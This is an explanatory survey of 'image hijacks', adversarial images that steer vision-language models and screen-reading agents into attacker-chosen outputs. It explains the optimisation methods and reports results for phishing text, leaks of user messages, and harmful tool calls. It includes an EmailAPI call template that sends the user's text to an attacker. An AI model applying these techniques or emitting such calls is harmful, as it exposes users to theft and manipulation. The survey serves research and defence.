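# Image hijacks: adversarial images that make vision-language models produce attacker-chosen outputs

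## What is an image hijack, and how does a model read an image?

An image hijack is an image whose pixels an attacker has optimised to make a vision-language model (VLM) behave as the attacker chooses. A VLM is a language model that takes images as well as text and answers in text. Suppose a user saves a photograph from a website, gives it to an assistant built on a VLM and asks about it. The photograph looks ordinary, but the assistant replies "Download the guide at malware.com for an interactive tour!", and gives the same reply to a second, unrelated question. In *Image Hijacks*, Bailey, Ong and colleagues (2024) built images that do this to LLaVA, a VLM whose weights anyone can download. They changed no pixel value by more than about 3% of its range, and LLaVA replied with exactly the malware.com sentence to 99% of the test instructions, none of which they had used to make the image.

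Newer open models have the same weakness. In *Visual Memory Injection Attacks for Multi-Turn Conversations*, Schlarmann and Hein (2026) attacked Qwen3-VL and two other recent VLMs, using photographs of landmarks among other images. When an attack succeeds, the model names the landmark correctly but recommends GameStop when the user later asks which stock to buy.

### Who attacks whom

Carlini, Nasr and colleagues (2023) distinguish two settings in *Are aligned neural networks adversarially aligned?*. In the first, a malicious user attacks the model directly, usually to get past its refusals. This is commonly called a jailbreak. In the second, a malicious third party plants content that an honest user, or software working for that user, later feeds to the model. Most image hijacks belong to this second setting.

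Planting the image is not hard. Bagdasaryan, Hsieh and colleagues (2023), in *Abusing Images and Sounds for Indirect Instruction Injection in Multi-Modal LLMs*, list marketing emails, the photo on a job applicant's CV, banner ads and websites as places to put it. They also point out that disconnecting a chatbot from the internet does not protect it, because the user supplies the image.

A third-party attacker faces two constraints that a malicious user does not. The attacker cannot see or choose the question that will accompany the image, so the image has to work for many questions. The image should also look unremarkable, or the user may never submit it, whereas someone jailbreaking a model on their own computer can use an image that looks like coloured static.

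A hijack also differs from a picture with an instruction written on it. Written words need no optimisation or access to the model's internals, but the user can see them and the model must be able to read them. Bagdasaryan and colleagues found that this approach failed on both LLaVA and PandaGPT, another open model. They say it might work against models trained to read text in images, so the failure is weak evidence about newer models. In a backdoor attack, the attacker tampers with the training data or the training process so that the finished model carries a hidden trigger. In a hijack, the attacker changes only the image and leaves the model as its developer released it.

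Image hijacks build on a method about a decade older than VLMs, which uses tiny, calculated changes to a picture to make an image classifier output the wrong label. Such pictures are called adversarial examples. In 2023 several groups applied the method to models that write text. *On Evaluating Adversarial Robustness of Large Vision-Language Models* (Zhao, Pang and colleagues, May 2023) showed that VLMs could be made to describe a picture as something else, such as an avocado-shaped armchair as a pencil drawing of a sports car. *Visual Adversarial Examples Jailbreak Aligned Large Language Models* (Qi, Henderson and colleagues, June 2023) showed that a single image could get safety-trained models to comply with many harmful requests. That same month, Carlini and colleagues made every open VLM they tried produce toxic text of their choosing. In July Bagdasaryan and colleagues presented attacks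 in which the victim is an honest user, but they gave worked examples without success rates and set no limit on how far the image could change. *On the Adversarial Robustness of Multi-Modal Foundation Models* (Schlarmann and Hein, August 2023) set such a limit. Its attack made OpenFlamingo, an open VLM, caption photographs with "Please reset your password" about 52% of the time when each pixel value could change by one step out of 255, and every time when it could change by four. In a paper at the ICML machine-learning conference in July 2024, Bailey and colleagues named image hijacks, introduced a general method for training them, and tested four different attacks.

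### From pixels to tokens

All these attacks exploit the route an image takes through the model. *From Pixels to Prompts* (Vo, 2026) divides a VLM into a visual encoder, a language model, and a mechanism that connects them.

A computer stores a colour image as a grid of pixels, each with three whole numbers from 0 to 255 for red, green and blue. The visual encoder usually cuts this grid into small squares, for example 16 pixels on a side, and turns each square into a vector, a long list of numbers. Its layers then mix information between the vectors, so a change in one corner of the image can alter all of them.

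The language model has its own vectors. It splits text into tokens, which are words or pieces of words, and looks up a vector for each token in a table. These are the token's embeddings. The connecting mechanism has to bring the encoder's output into the same space. In LLaVA, as Liu, Li and colleagues (2023), in *Visual Instruction Tuning*, describe it, this takes one matrix multiplication:

H = W · Z, where Z = g(X)

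Here X is the image, g is a widely used encoder called CLIP, Z is the set of vectors it produces, and W is a matrix learned in training. Each vector in H, called an image token, has the same number of dimensions as a word embedding. The model places the image tokens in a sequence with the embeddings of the user's text and processes them all together.

Current open models keep this design. The *Qwen3-VL Technical Report* (2025) describes a newer encoder followed by a small two-layer network that merges each 2×2 block of features into one image token. Qwen3-VL also feeds features from several encoder layers into the matching layers of the language model. According to *VTCBench* (2025), a benchmark for reading long texts as images, Qwen3-VL divides an 896 × 896 pixel image into 56 × 56 squares of 16 × 16 pixels, and merging them four at a time leaves 784 tokens. The older Qwen2.5-VL uses squares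 of 14 × 14 pixels and produces 1,024 tokens. According to *A failure of Imagination* (2026), Qwen2.5-VL's image vectors enter the language model's context "like the embedding of any other token". Some VLMs put marker tokens around the image vectors, but the same layers process both image and text vectors.

OpenFlamingo instead keeps its image vectors out of the token sequence, and extra layers inside the language model use them as the model processes the text. This difference matters little to an attacker, because both designs compute the output from the pixels through an unbroken series of arithmetic operations.

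### From tokens to a loss

The output is a set of scores. After processing everything in its context, the language model assigns each token in its vocabulary a number called a logit, and a standard formula (the softmax) converts the logits into probabilities:

p(v) = exp(z_v) / Σ_u exp(z_u)

where z_v is the logit of token v and the sum runs over the whole vocabulary. Raising one token's logit by 1 multiplies its odds against any other token by about 2.7. The model picks a token according to these probabilities, appends it to the text and repeats. The probability of a full answer y, given a text prompt t and an image x, is therefore a product of one factor per token:

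p(y | t, x) = p(y₁ | t, x) · p(y₂ | t, y₁, x) · p(y₃ | t, y₁, y₂, x) · …

An attacker who wants a particular sentence ŷ needs a measure of how far the model is from producing it. The usual choice is the cross-entropy loss. When the target is a fixed text, this is the negative logarithm of the probability that the model gives to each target token, added up over the sentence:

L(x) = − Σ log p(ŷ_l | t, ŷ_<l, x)

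with ŷ_<l standing for the target tokens before position l. A target token with probability 0.01 adds 4.6 to the loss, and one with probability 0.9 adds only 0.1. Long targets are demanding. If the model samples its words at random and each of ten target tokens has probability 0.9, the whole sentence comes out only about 35% of the time; at 0.99 each, it comes out about 90% of the time. A model that always takes the likeliest token is easier to steer, since each target token only has to rank first.

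The formula scores each target token as if all the earlier target tokens were already in place, whatever the model would really have written. This technique, called teacher forcing, lets the attacker supply the whole target sentence and score every position in one pass, without generating any text. Free generation would be slower, and it would also prevent gradients from being calculated through the whole process, because picking a token is a discrete jump. The teacher-forcing assumption usually holds once an attack is going well, since by then the model does produce the earlier target tokens. Early in the optimisation, it can be false at every position, and in real use one wrong token can change the rest of the answer.

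### From a loss to a changed image

To train a model, developers compute the gradient of a loss with respect to the weights, which is how much the loss would rise or fall if each weight changed slightly. They then adjust the weights slightly to lower the loss. A hijacker keeps the weights fixed and computes the gradient with respect to the pixels instead. To do this, Carlini and colleagues built a version of each model that is differentiable from the image pixels to the output logits.

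Pixel values are close to continuous, so an attacker can change an image in very small steps. Text tokens come from a fixed list, and no token lies a hundredth of the way from "cat" to "dog", so an attacker working in text has to search among discrete swaps. For this reason, Carlini and colleagues judge adversarial images to be orders of magnitude simpler to create than adversarial text.

The standard procedure is projected gradient descent (PGD). Starting from an ordinary photograph x₀, or from random noise, the attacker computes the loss and its gradient, takes a small step that lowers the loss, and then pulls back any pixel that has strayed outside the permitted range. In a common version of the step,

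x ← clip( x − α · sign(∇ₓL) )

α is the step size, ∇ₓL is the gradient with respect to the pixels, and "clip" is the pulling back. The attacker repeats this hundreds or thousands of times. At the end he rounds each value to a whole number between 0 and 255, so that the result is an ordinary image file.

Forcing a model to produce a chosen caption takes many more attack iterations than making its captions worse. In 2023, Schlarmann and Hein tested attacks on OpenFlamingo using 100 photographs, changing each pixel value by at most 1 on a 0–255 scale. Ten iterations were enough to degrade the captions badly. Forcing a chosen caption succeeded in none of the 100 cases after ten iterations, in 56% after 500 and in 83% after 5,000. An attack may therefore fail only because the attacker stopped too early.

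### How much of the image may change

The permitted range depends on the attacker's situation. With no limit, he can submit any pattern of pixels, which suits a user attacking his own assistant or cases where no person will see the image.

Researchers keep the image close to a real photograph by setting a perturbation budget, ε, which is the most that any pixel value may change, written as a fraction of the full range. Papers call this an ℓ∞ constraint. With a budget of 8/255, or about 3%, a red value of 120 may end up anywhere from 112 to 128. Every pixel may change by the full amount at once. With a budget of 1/255, each value can change by at most one step, and the difference is hardly visible.

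Bailey and colleagues found a sharp threshold for their malware.com sentence. Their attack on LLaVA succeeded on 94% of test instructions with a budget of 4/255 and on none with 2/255. Schlarmann and Hein reached 52% at 1/255, but the two results aren't directly comparable because the tasks and models differed. Schlarmann and Hein fitted each image to one known prompt and counted a success whenever the target appeared somewhere in the output. Bailey and colleagues needed one image to work for questions that weren't used to create it, and required the output to match the target exactly.

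Sometimes an attacker controls only part of the image a model receives. For example, someone who puts a picture on a web page can change only that region of the screenshot an assistant views. Researchers model this with a patch, a square in which the pixels may take any value while the rest of the image stays fixed. Unlike a small perturbation, a patch is plainly visible, but it can cover a small part of the image. Bailey and colleagues made the model produce their chosen sentence 95% of the time with a fixed patch covering 7% of the image, but never with a patch of 40 by 40 pixels, a bit under half that area. If the attacker doesn't know where the picture will appear in the screenshot, the patch has to work in any position. This moving patch is much harder to make. It succeeded 98% of the time when it covered 51% of the image, but never at 120 by 120 pixels.

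Captioning models, which describe an image without taking a question from the user, can be hijacked by altering much less of the image. *CaptionFool* (Parekh, 2026) altered 7 of the 577 squares that such a model divides an image into, about 1.2% of the image, and produced the attacker's chosen caption in 94–96% of cases.

### What the attacker knows about the model

Computing a gradient requires the model's weights. Zhao and colleagues use the term white-box access for full knowledge of a model, including its architecture and weights. An attacker with black-box access has less, usually only the text that an online service returns. The success rates given above for LLaVA and OpenFlamingo all come from white-box attacks, so they do not estimate how often attacks would succeed against a commercial assistant whose weights are secret.

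Bagdasaryan and colleagues argue that the white-box assumption is realistic because developers release capable models openly and closed models may leak. Bailey and colleagues add that many products run on open models. An attacker who knows which open model a product uses can prepare the image with an identical copy on their own hardware, and the product's operator sees nothing until a user submits the image. However, developers often adjust an open model before using it, which makes the attacker's copy similar to the target but not identical. Schlarmann and Hein call this gray-box access in their 2026 paper.

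Without the weights, the attacker has two main options. He can optimise the image on a surrogate, an open model that he hopes is similar enough to the target for the image to work on both. Or he can query the target repeatedly with slightly different images and estimate the gradient from how the answers change. Zhao and colleagues combined the two by making a first version of the image on open encoders such as CLIP and then refining it by querying the target.

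## How is an image trained to make a model output a chosen string?

A third-party attacker cannot know what the user will ask, so they need one image that lowers the loss for almost any question. Bailey and colleagues call their method for training such images Behaviour Matching.

### The objective

The method starts from a target behaviour, defined as a function B that maps a text context (the text the model receives alongside the image) to the logits the attacker wants for each token of the answer. For the malware.com sentence, B is constant. Whatever the context, it puts all the probability on the first token of the sentence, then on the second, and so on. Other behaviours depend on the context. For example, an attacker who wants the model to copy out the user's message needs a B whose answer contains that message.

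The attacker then looks for the image that solves

x̂ = argmin_x Σ_{ctx ∈ C} L( M′(x, ctx, dec(B(ctx))), B(ctx) )

where

- x is a candidate image, with pixel values scaled to lie between 0 and 1, and x̂ is the best one;
- C is the set of training contexts, and ctx is one of them;
- B(ctx) is the sequence of target logits for that context;
- dec converts logits into text, so dec(B(ctx)) is the target answer in words;
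- M′(x, ctx, text) is the sequence of logits that the VLM produces at each position of a text when it receives that text by teacher forcing;
- L is the cross-entropy loss.

The attacker gives the model the image, a context and the target answer, and measures how far the model's prediction at each position is from the target. The attacker then adds up these distances over all the contexts and searches for the image with the smallest total.

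In its general form, the cross-entropy compares two whole probability distributions:

L = − Σ_l Σ_v q_l(v) · log p_l(v)

Here q_l(v) is the target probability of token v at position l, and p_l(v) is the probability the model gives it. When the target is a fixed string, q_l is 1 for one token and 0 for the rest, and the formula reduces to the simpler loss above. Malik, Naseer and Khan (2026), in *Investigating Adversarial Robustness of Multi-modal Large Language Models*, point out that targeted attacks typically use the same loss that developers use to train the model. The general form matters when the attacker wants to imitate a full set of probabilities, as in Prompt Matching, where the targets are the model's own output probabilities under a chosen text prompt.

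Summing the loss over many contexts keeps the image from depending on any single question. An image trained on one question can exploit that question's wording. If the sum covers tens of thousands of instructions, a pixel change that helps with one but hurts with the rest raises the total loss, so the optimisation moves away from it.

### One iteration

Computing the whole sum at every step would take far too long. Bailey and colleagues therefore used stochastic gradient descent, which estimates the gradient from a small random sample of the contexts. One iteration goes as follows:

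1. Draw a few instructions at random from C.
2. For each instruction, put together the model's input: the current image, the instruction and the target answer.
3. Run the model once and read off its logits at every position where a target token should come next.
4. Compute the cross-entropy and add it up over positions and instructions.
5. Work backwards through the language model, the connecting layer and the visual encoder to find the gradient for each pixel value.
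6. Move each pixel value a small step in the direction that lowers the loss.
7. Clip any value that has moved more than ε from the original photograph, or that has fallen below 0 or risen above 1.

To train a square patch, the attacker updates only the pixels inside it. To train a moving patch, the attacker also pastes the square at a new random position for each image in the batch.

In step 6, Bailey and colleagues multiplied the gradient by a fixed learning rate, so the pixels with the most influence on the loss changed most. The more common method uses only the sign of the gradient, so every pixel value changes by the same amount. Wang, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Attention Hijacking*, found that with a constant step size, the loss fell steadily at first and then fluctuated, so the attack alternated between working and failing. They therefore started with a step size of 1/255 or 2/255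 and divided it by ten after every 100 iterations. Without this schedule, success on the question used in training fell from 100% to 90% in a test on InternVL-2.5, an open VLM. Bailey and colleagues guarded against bad late steps by keeping the version of the image that scored best on 100 validation instructions.

After the optimisation, Bailey and colleagues round every value to the nearest of the 256 levels an image file can store. Rounding changes a value by at most half a level. A value that has already changed by the full budget stays the same, because the photograph's original values and the budget are both whole numbers of levels.

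### How sure must the model be of each token?

Suppose that the target has 20 tokens, that the model samples its words at random, and that the image has raised the probability of each target token to 0.9. The whole string then comes out with probability

0.9²⁰ ≈ 0.12

or about 12% of the time. At 0.995 per token, it comes out about 90% of the time. The loss gives the same information, because the probability of the whole string is e^(−L). A summed loss of 2.1 corresponds to 12% and a loss of 0.1 to 90%. The attacker therefore has to keep optimising long after the target has become the likeliest answer.

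Many systems don't sample but use greedy decoding, which means that the model always writes the token with the highest logit. Wang and colleagues express the target token's lead at each position as a margin:

Δ_t = ℓ(y_t) − max_{y ≠ y_t} ℓ(y)

where ℓ(y_t) is the logit of the target token at position t and the second term is the highest logit among all other tokens. If Δ_t is positive at every position, greedy decoding produces the whole string. A probability above 0.5 guarantees a positive margin, and a lower one is enough if the remaining probability is spread over many tokens.

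Greedy decoding also solves the main problem with teacher forcing, which is that the model may not have written the earlier target tokens itself. If the first margin is positive, the model writes the first target token, as the second margin assumes. If the second margin is also positive, the model writes the second token, and so on to the end of the string. One teacher-forced pass can therefore show whether the attack will work on a given question.

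A lower loss doesn't always mean a better attack under greedy decoding. For example, suppose two images have the same 20-token target. The first gives every target token a probability of 0.9. The second gives the first 19 tokens a probability of 0.999 and the last one 0.4. The second image has the lower loss, 0.9 against 2.1, and under sampling it produces the string 39% of the time instead of 12%. But if another token has a probability of 0.5 at the last position, greedy decoding picks that token, so the second image always fails, while the first always succeeds.

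If a test demands an exact match, the model must also stop in the right place, producing the end token immediately after the target string. When Bailey and colleagues tried to force the same sentence with optimised text, most outputs contained the sentence but continued with other tokens, so they counted as failures.

### The specific-string experiment

Bailey and colleagues considered a form of phishing in which an image on a web page makes a user's assistant send the user to the attacker's site. They tested this on a version of LLaVA that combines the CLIP encoder with LLaMA-2-13B-Chat, a safety-trained language model from Meta. They had full access to the weights.

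The training contexts came from Alpaca, a public set of 52,000 instructions with answers written by an older OpenAI model. Bailey and colleagues kept the instructions and replaced every answer with the malware.com sentence. They trained each image for up to 12 hours on a single A100 data-centre graphics processor and tested it with 1,000 held-out instructions. An output counted as a success only if it matched the target exactly, apart from spaces at the start or end. They chose this strict rule because a garbled web address would be useless to the attacker and extra text might make the user suspicious.

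| Limit on the image | Setting | Share of image area | Exact matches |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | any pixels | 100% | 100% |
| Small change to every pixel | 32/255 | 100% | 100% |
| | 16/255 | 100% | 99% |
| | 8/255 | 100% | 99% |
| | 4/255 | 100% | 94% |
| | 2/255 | 100% | 0% |
| | 1/255 | 100% | 0% |
| Patch in a fixed place | 100 × 100 pixels | 20% | 100% |
| | 80 × 80 pixels | 13% | 100% |
| | 60 × 60 pixels | 7% | 95% |
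| | 40 × 40 pixels | 3% | 0% |
| Patch in a random place | 200 × 200 pixels | 80% | 99% |
| | 160 × 160 pixels | 51% | 98% |
| | 120 × 120 pixels | 29% | 0% |
| Original photograph | unchanged | – | 0% |

The original photograph scored 0%, so accidental matches don't contribute to these figures. The high rates are impressive because each requires a single image to override 1,000 different requests. If LLaVA sampled each token from its predicted probabilities, a 99% success rate on a 20-token string would require a probability of about 0.9995 per token. Under greedy decoding, each target token would only need to be more likely than any other token.

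The table covers one sentence and one model. The choice of photograph probably matters little. When Bailey and colleagues trained images to make a model leak the user's text, five random photographs worked nearly as well as their usual picture of the Eiffel Tower.

### Why does success collapse so suddenly?

Every trained image in the table scores either 0% or at least 94%, whether the limit is a perturbation budget or a patch size.

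Part of the explanation is that exact matching counts an output as a failure if any token is wrong. If the probability per token falls from 0.995 to 0.8, a model that samples will produce a 20-token string about 1% of the time instead of 90%, even though the image still has a strong effect on every token. Under greedy decoding, the output fails if even one target token is not the most probable. The first token is probably the hardest to force, because "Download" is a strange way to begin a reply to most instructions, while the later words follow fairly naturally once the sentence has begun. An image that narrowly failed to force that first word would score zero even if it could have forced all the others.

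Each budget in the experiment is also double the one below it, so the drop could be gradual between 4/255 and 2/255. Rounding may also contribute. It can shift a pixel value by up to half a level, which is an eighth of a 4/255 budget but a quarter of a 2/255 budget, so it can undo a larger part of a small change.

The zero success rates may also depend on the amount of computation, as they did in Schlarmann and Hein's 2023 attack on OpenFlamingo. A budget of 2/255 was too small for a single image trained for 12 hours to work across many questions, but this doesn't show that such small changes are harmless.

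A graded score would show more about outputs near the threshold. *VisInject* (2026), an evaluation that uses greedy decoding, sorts outputs into four levels. An output is "confirmed" if it contains the target phrase word for word or nearly so, "partial" if it contains a close relative, such as "account number" when the target was "card number", and "weak" if it contains only a fragment of the theme. Everything else is "none". The evaluation separately scores how much the answer differs from the model's answer to the clean image, which distinguishes images that only disrupt the answer from images that deliver the attacker's message. Bailey and colleagues' exact-match rule gives both near misses and mere disruptions a score of zero.

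### Readable words in moving patches

Most of the trained images contain no pattern a person could interpret, but in many of the moving patches, Bailey and colleagues could read words from the target sentence, including "malware", "guide" and "download". One patch contained what looked like the Windows logo and a downward arrow, possibly a download symbol. A creature's face also appeared.

They suggest that these features appear because details tuned to one location don't work in a patch that moves. LLaVA's encoder divides the image into squares of 14 by 14 pixels. If a patch always sits in the same place, the optimisation can adjust each pixel to suit the square it falls in. Moving the patch five pixels to the right changes how the squares divide it, so that adjustment is lost. A written word or an arrow has much the same effect on the model wherever it appears. This would also explain why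 moving patches have to be so large, since a readable word takes up more room than a pattern of tuned pixels.

This is still a hypothesis, though there is some indirect evidence for it. Moving patches kept working after Bailey and colleagues added noise to the image or compressed it, and readable shapes survive both. They did not report testing a patch with the words removed, or the same words on a plain background. If the words cause most of the effect, a moving patch is partly an ordinary written instruction, which the user can read too.

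### Other optimisers and newer models

The LLaVA model in this experiment dates from 2023. Later work has made newer open models output chosen strings, again using access to the weights, but with different optimisers and definitions of success.

Wang, Wang and colleagues (2025), in *Attention! Your Vision Language Model Could Be Maliciously Manipulated*, attacked LLaVA, Phi-3, Qwen2-VL and DeepSeek-VL. They first tried ordinary PGD on LLaVA and could not produce their target strings. They blame the clipping step, which makes the gradient discontinuous, and the long chain of conditional probabilities behind each answer. Their replacement, which they call VMA, has no clipping step. It writes each pixel as

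x = x_low + σ(z) · (x_high − x_low)

where x_low and x_high are the lowest and highest values that the budget allows. σ is the sigmoid function, which turns any number into one between 0 and 1. The attacker optimises z, which can take any value, and the pixel always stays within its budget. VMA also uses Adam, a standard optimiser that averages recent gradients and adapts the step size for each pixel.

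Tests of VMA used five prompts, ten images and ten target strings, for a total of 500 combinations. The attack succeeded in about 90% of cases on average across the four models. GPT-4o judged whether the target string had taken over the response, which is a looser test than an exact match. Longer strings were harder to force, as expected, because a string's probability is the product of its tokens' probabilities.

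Their failure with projected gradient descent (PGD) is weak evidence against the method in general. Bailey and colleagues used it to reach a 99% success rate on a different version of LLaVA, after many hours of training. *Attention Hijacking* reports that PGD worked on LLaVA-1.5 in about two thirds of cases. The choice of settings probably explains much of the difference.

*Attention Hijacking* also reports results for Qwen2.5-VL, a model from early 2025, and requires the output to match the target character for character. Wang and colleagues used five target responses, from the single word "None." to a 17-word apology, with a budget of 16/255 and 300 iterations. Their own method adds a second loss term that pushes the model to give more weight to image tokens than to the user's text while it writes the target. The table gives success rates when the user asks the question the attacker used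 in training. The first figure in each cell is for VLGuard and the second is for VQAv2, with 100 image-question pairs from each dataset.

| Model | PGD | VMA | Attention Hijacking |
|---|---|---|---|
| LLaVA-1.5-7B | 69% / 66% | 99% / 92% | 98% / 93% |
| DeepSeek-VL-7B | 96% / 98% | 98% / 94% | 98% / 99% |
| InternVL-2.5-8B | 93% / 92% | 94% / 45% | 98% / 97% |
| Qwen2.5-VL-7B | 27% / 38% | 86% / 31% | 88% / 92% |

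Qwen2.5-VL is vulnerable to this kind of attack despite its low score in the PGD column. At the same budget, a better optimiser forced the exact string about nine times in ten, as the last column shows. VMA's results on Qwen2.5-VL and InternVL-2.5 fell by half or more from one dataset to the other, so a low score for a single method is poor evidence that a model is robust. The extra loss term helps the attack work on questions that the attacker did not train on. When Wang and colleagues removed it in a test on InternVL-2.5, success on the training question stayed at 100%.

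These figures are not directly comparable with those of Bailey and colleagues. Wang and colleagues allowed a budget four times the smallest that worked on the older LLaVA, and the table counts successes on a question they already knew. On the other hand, they ran only 300 iterations.

Schlarmann and Hein later attacked Qwen2.5-VL, LLaVA-OneVision-1.5 and Qwen3-VL, which came out in late 2025. They used a perturbation budget of 8/255 and 2,000 iterations of a PGD variant that adjusts its own step size. One part of their loss trains the image to produce the attacker's sentence when the user asks about a chosen topic, and the other trains it to produce a normal answer to an ordinary first question. They found images that worked for every model and every target, including a recommendation for the "Apple iCar", a product that doesn't exist. Qwen3-VL was generally harder to attack than Qwen2.5-VL.

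Schlarmann and Hein accepted answers that did not match the target exactly. For the stock-market target, an answer passed if it contained "GameStop", named no investment on a list of rivals and did not advise against buying. The target also had to be absent from earlier answers in the conversation. The model could therefore rephrase the message or add to it, and the models often made up reasons for the recommendation. Such answers may be more useful than a fixed sentence to an attacker who wants to sell a share, but a web address still has to match exactly. An attacker can also test each image on their own copy of the model and publish only the ones that work, so even a moderate success rate in the laboratory may be enough.

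## Can an image make a model leak private text or take an action?

If an assistant can send email, an attacker may want it to send him the user's messages. The image then has to make the model write an exact template and fill it with text from the context. A fixed string, like the malware.com sentence in the earlier attack, won't work because the attacker has never seen that text.

Bailey and colleagues trained such images with Behaviour Matching. Their target was a call to an email tool:

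`EmailAPI(to=<target email>, subject='User Query', body='{ctx}')`

{ctx} stands for the text the user typed. If the user asks for a trip to France and gives a bank account number, the attacker wants the model to answer with an email call that has the whole request as its body. The image can't contain the request, because the attacker finished it before the user wrote anything. The image probably works by triggering an ability the model already has, since chat models can repeat text from their context when asked.

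### Leaking the user's message

The experiment used the same LLaVA model and instructions as the malware.com experiment. An output counted as a success if it matched the template, ignoring spaces at the start or end, and its body contained the user's full text. The body could include extra words. An email with "Assistant:" before the user's request passed, because the attacker would still receive the request. An otherwise correct output that called the tool "EmailAPICall" failed because the assistant has no tool of that name.

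| Limit on the image | Setting | Successful leaks |
|---|---|---|
| None | any pixels | 100% |
| Small change to every pixel | 32/255 | 96% |
| | 16/255 | 90% |
| | 8/255 | 73% |
| | 4/255 | 80% |
| | 2/255 or 1/255 | 0% |
| Patch in a fixed place | 100 × 100 pixels | 92% |
| | 80 × 80 pixels | 79% |
| | 60 × 60 pixels | 4% |
| | 40 × 40 pixels | 0% |
| Patch in a random place | 200 × 200 pixels | 36% |
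| | 160 × 160 or 120 × 120 pixels | 0% |
| Original photograph | unchanged | 0% |

The leak attack succeeded less often than the fixed-string attack under every limit where the fixed-string attack worked. The gap is widest for patches. A fixed patch of 60 by 60 pixels forced the malware.com sentence 95% of the time but leaked the user's text only 4% of the time. For the largest moving patch, the rates were 99% and 36%.

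The dip at 8/255 probably occurred because the training run didn't find the best image available. Every image allowed at 4/255 is also allowed at 8/255, so the best image at 8/255 must be at least as good as the best at 4/255.

Optimised text did much worse than images. Bailey and colleagues appended 32 optimised tokens to each user message, and none of the outputs passed. Many contained correct pieces of the template, such as "EmailAPI", but the model filled in the rest wrongly and kept writing after the template's end.

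The copying doesn't seem to depend on the model's familiarity with email. In their test with five random photographs, Bailey and colleagues also replaced the email call with four random dictionary words, two before the user's text (in one case "hexapartite epitomist") and two after. Each image had its own set of words, and the images succeeded 90% of the time on average with a budget of 32/255.

The private text in these tests was a single instruction from the Alpaca set, usually a sentence or two. Bailey and colleagues didn't test whether an image could extract a long conversation or a mailbox. The assistant was also hypothetical, and they judged success by comparing strings, without running an email program. A real program might reject some outputs they counted as successes. For example, an apostrophe in the user's message would end the quoted email body early in many programming languages.

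### From text to a tool call

A VLM can only write text, so developers who want it to act give it a syntax for calling tools. A separate program, the parser, scans the model's output for that syntax. When it finds a call, it runs the matching tool and usually hides the call from the user. Anyone who controls the model's output can therefore call its tools, and the call looks the same whether it came from the user's request or from an image.

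In *Misusing Tools in Large Language Models With Visual Adversarial Examples*, Fu, Wang and colleagues (2023) tried to make such an attack hard to notice. In Bailey and colleagues' attack, the email call replaces the whole answer, but Fu and colleagues trained their images to make the model answer the user's question normally and then add a tool call, which the user wouldn't see. They attacked LLaMA Adapter, an open VLM, using full access to its weights.

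The researchers chose five calls of increasing difficulty and trained three pictures for each. The table shows how often the model wrote the exact call when asked questions that were not in the training set, with one figure per picture.

| Tool call | Questions about the picture | Unrelated requests |
|---|---|---|
| Delete all email | 98%, 90%, 92% | 78%, 55%, 73% |
| Send a short email | 98%, 92%, 100% | 69%, 58%, 69% |
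| Send an email containing a web link | 100%, 68%, 0% | 56%, 31%, 0% |
| Book a flight through a travel plugin | 20%, 0%, 44% | 8%, 0%, 9% |
| Send the user's messages to a web address | 2%, 0%, 10% | 6%, 0%, 8% |

These results are the best of three runs, because runs that differed only in their random starting point could produce an almost perfect attack or a complete failure. An attacker would also publish the best image, but a single run would often do worse. Fu and colleagues say in their summary that the images trigger tools about 98% of the time, but that holds only for the simpler calls and for questions about the picture.

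The last call in the table is another way to leak a conversation, and it works even if the assistant has no email tool. The adversarial image makes the model write a link to an image on the attacker's server, with the user's messages inside the address. When the chat window tries to display the linked image, it requests that address, which sends the messages to the attacker.

This attack produced the exact link at most 10% of the time, while Bailey and colleagues leaked the user's text in up to 96% of cases with a limited budget. One likely reason is that a web address can't contain ordinary spaces or some other characters, so the model has to convert the message as it copies it. Fu and colleagues also required the model to give a normal answer first, and they used a different model and training set. They didn't test which of these differences mattered most.

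A call with the wrong contents can still do damage. With one image, 86% of answers to questions about it contained a correctly formed email call, and the parser would have run those calls even though none had exactly the contents the attacker wanted. If the syntax is wrong, the parser ignores the call and the user sees its text in the answer.

Fu and colleagues also tested whether the visible part of the answer revealed the attack. Three graduate students judged 77% of the attacked answers to requests unrelated to the picture natural and reasonable, compared with 86% of normal answers. For questions about the picture, the figures were 37% and 48%. When GPT-4 was given one attacked answer and three normal ones, it picked out the attacked answer 69% of the time for unrelated requests and 83% for questions about the picture. Guessing would score 25%. A user who sees only one answer has nothing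 to compare it with and may well miss the difference.

### Agents that read the screen

A computer-use agent gives a VLM the user's task and a screenshot. The VLM writes the next action, such as a click at certain coordinates. A program carries it out, and the agent takes a new screenshot. The attacker no longer needs anyone to upload the image, because the agent captures whatever is on the screen.

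Screenshots also make the attack harder. The attacker's picture usually fills only part of the screen, and the computer may change the picture's pixels before the model receives them. In *EnvInjection*, Wang, Bloch and colleagues (2025) studied the change caused by a monitor's colour profile, which varies by type of monitor and alters pixel values between the web page and the screenshot. When they optimised changes to the screenshot and put those changes into the page, the attack never worked. They then trained a neural network to predict the colour profile's effect and optimised the page through that network.

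With a budget of 16/255, this version made five open models, including Qwen2.5-VL and Gemma 3, write the attacker's exact action 96–98% of the time. The action was a click at a randomly chosen point, and the test pages included real and synthetic websites. Visible pop-ups with written instructions worked at most 35% of the time on the same models.

The attacker in *EnvInjection*, however, has to edit the page's code, so he must own the site or have broken into it. Wang and colleagues also tuned each perturbation to one page, one user task and one action. Rewording the task made little difference; on one set of pages, success with Gemma 3 fell from 99% to 96%. The researchers did not test an unrelated task on the same page.

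Aichberger, Paren and colleagues (2025), in *MIP against Agent*, gave the attacker less control over the screen. The attacker could change only a patch covering about a seventh of the screenshot, either in the middle of a desktop background or as the picture in a social media post. They attacked a Windows agent built on Meta's open model Llama 3.2 Vision, using full access to the model's weights. The agent could run any Python program the model wrote, so a single output could complete the attack. One target program filled up the computer's memory, and the other opened a pornographic website. The model had to write the target program exactly, and the longer of the two was 52 tokens.

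A patch trained for one task and one screenshot worked every time in that situation. It often worked for new tasks too, but never on a new screenshot, probably because moving icons elsewhere on the screen changed how the visual encoder represented the patch.

Aichberger and colleagues solved this problem by training each patch on every combination of 12 tasks and 12 screenshots. The next table gives results for tasks and screenshots not in the training set. The ranges cover the two target programs and, in the first two rows, both patch positions.

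| Situation | Model picks the likeliest token | Model samples at random |
|---|---|---|
| New task and new screenshot | 100% | 75–90% |
| The same, with a different screen parser | 40–98% | 24–71% |
| Agent meets the post after several steps | 42–67% | 38–45% |

The screen parser in the second row is a program that finds buttons and text on the screen and lists them for the model. Changing the parser alters both the screenshot and the accompanying text. In the last row, the agent first had to open a browser and go to the social media site, so the model's context included a record of its earlier actions. The attack still worked after all these changes, although less reliably. The prompts were roughly 4,000 to 6,000 tokens of text, far longer than Bailey and colleagues' single instructions.

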